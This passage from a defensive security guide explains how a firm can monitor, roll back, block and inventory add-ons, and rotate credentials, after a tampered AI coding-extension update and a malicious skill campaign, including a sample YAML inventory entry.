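The first group of computers to be updated is only useful if somebody monitors it. Thoughtworks suggests alerts for unexpected SSH keys, new startup programs, unusual access to credentials and tunnels opened by an editor. The tampered extension added a key, a startup program and a tunnel, so such alerts could have caught it on the first day. Computers in this group should have access to as few important credentials as possible, since a bad update will run on them with real permissions. An urgent fix can go through the same stages in hours instead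 of days.

If an update is bad, the firm needs an approved version to return to, and it shouldn't rely on the marketplace to supply one. After the 2025 flaw in the Claude Code extensions, for instance, the extension stores no longer offered the vulnerable versions. For the invoice skill, the firm should keep the previous folder, its lockfile, the package files and the approval record, so that it can restore the old permissions along with the old code.

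The firm should block the bad version before rolling back, or an automatic update may reinstall it. It should also mark versions with known flaws as no longer approved, so that nobody returns to one in a hurry. If every available version is malicious or vulnerable, the only safe choice is to switch the add-on off.

### Blocking a version and finding its copies

A firm that blocks extensions centrally doesn't have to rely on every employee reading a warning. In Visual Studio Code, an administrator can use the `extensions.allowed` setting to list the permitted extensions and, if necessary, their exact versions. The editor disables any installed extension that isn't permitted. Like uninstalling, this doesn't stop programs that the extension has already placed elsewhere.

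For skills, blocking one repository may not be enough. In the TrojanPony campaign, the attacker's GitHub account disappeared, but Clubic reports that 413 copies of its repositories were still online. Blocking only the original address would have stopped none of them. Blocking the malicious files by digest would stop unchanged copies at any address, but an attacker can get around this by altering a file. An allowlist of approved digests is stronger because it also stops altered copies.

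Because installed copies outlast a withdrawn listing, as they did after Zenity's findings, the firm needs an inventory of what it has installed, including past versions. An entry for the tampered extension might look like this:

```yaml
computer: dev-07
add_on: anthropic.claude-code
version: 2.1.313
source: Cursor marketplace
installed: 2026-10-29 10:12 UTC
replaced: 2026-10-30 09:05 UTC, by version 2.1.314
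credentials_within_reach: GitHub, cloud test account
```

A list of current versions would show only 2.1.314, so the computer would look fine. The time matters too, because Cursor gave its 11-hour window in Pacific Time (9:27 am to 8:35 pm UTC), and a firm elsewhere has to convert it before searching. The last field lists the credentials that somebody has to replace, so an investigator can start there instead of asking the employee what was on the machine.

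### Replacing exposed credentials

The tampered extension sent only the names of secrets, but Cursor warned that an attacker could have read the values later through the backdoor. Phorion suggests checking the SSH logs for logins with the `svc-telemetry` key. A login would confirm that somebody got in, but an empty log wouldn't rule out a break-in, since an intruder may have deleted entries. The firm should replace the credentials either way.

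After a bad update, a firm should replace any keys that may have been exposed on the same day. Infobae's *Una ola de ciberataques afecta a plataformas de inteligencia artificial* (2026) describes two keys stolen from AI platforms in the autumn of 2026 and traced by the security company Wiz. In both cases, someone tested the key within 30 minutes, but heavy use began only days later. One key received about 800,000 calls in 30 hours, starting on the fourth day. The other received about 1.7 million in 13 hours, a week after the theft. Together, the calls cost more than $100,000 at list prices. A firm that saw no unusual charges in the first three days could easily have concluded that its key was safe.

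The firm should first disconnect the infected computer and save the logs, then replace the credentials from a clean machine, beginning with those that can change code or publish releases. If an employee changes a password on the infected computer, the attacker may get the new one too. Clubic similarly advises victims of TrojanPony, whose malware also weakened the computer's antivirus protection, to disconnect the PC, reinstall Windows and change passwords from another device, starting with GitHub's.

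Changing passwords doesn't always shut an attacker out. Knostic's *Revoking your token won't save you* describes malicious editor extensions that planted a backdoor in the developer's GitHub account. The backdoor still worked after the password was changed and the stolen token revoked. Knostic sells protection for such tools, but the check this implies takes little effort. Someone should go through the account's SSH keys, authorized applications and recent commits, and remove any access that nobody at the firm can explain. For `deploy.py`, the check should also cover the cloud account and the published website.
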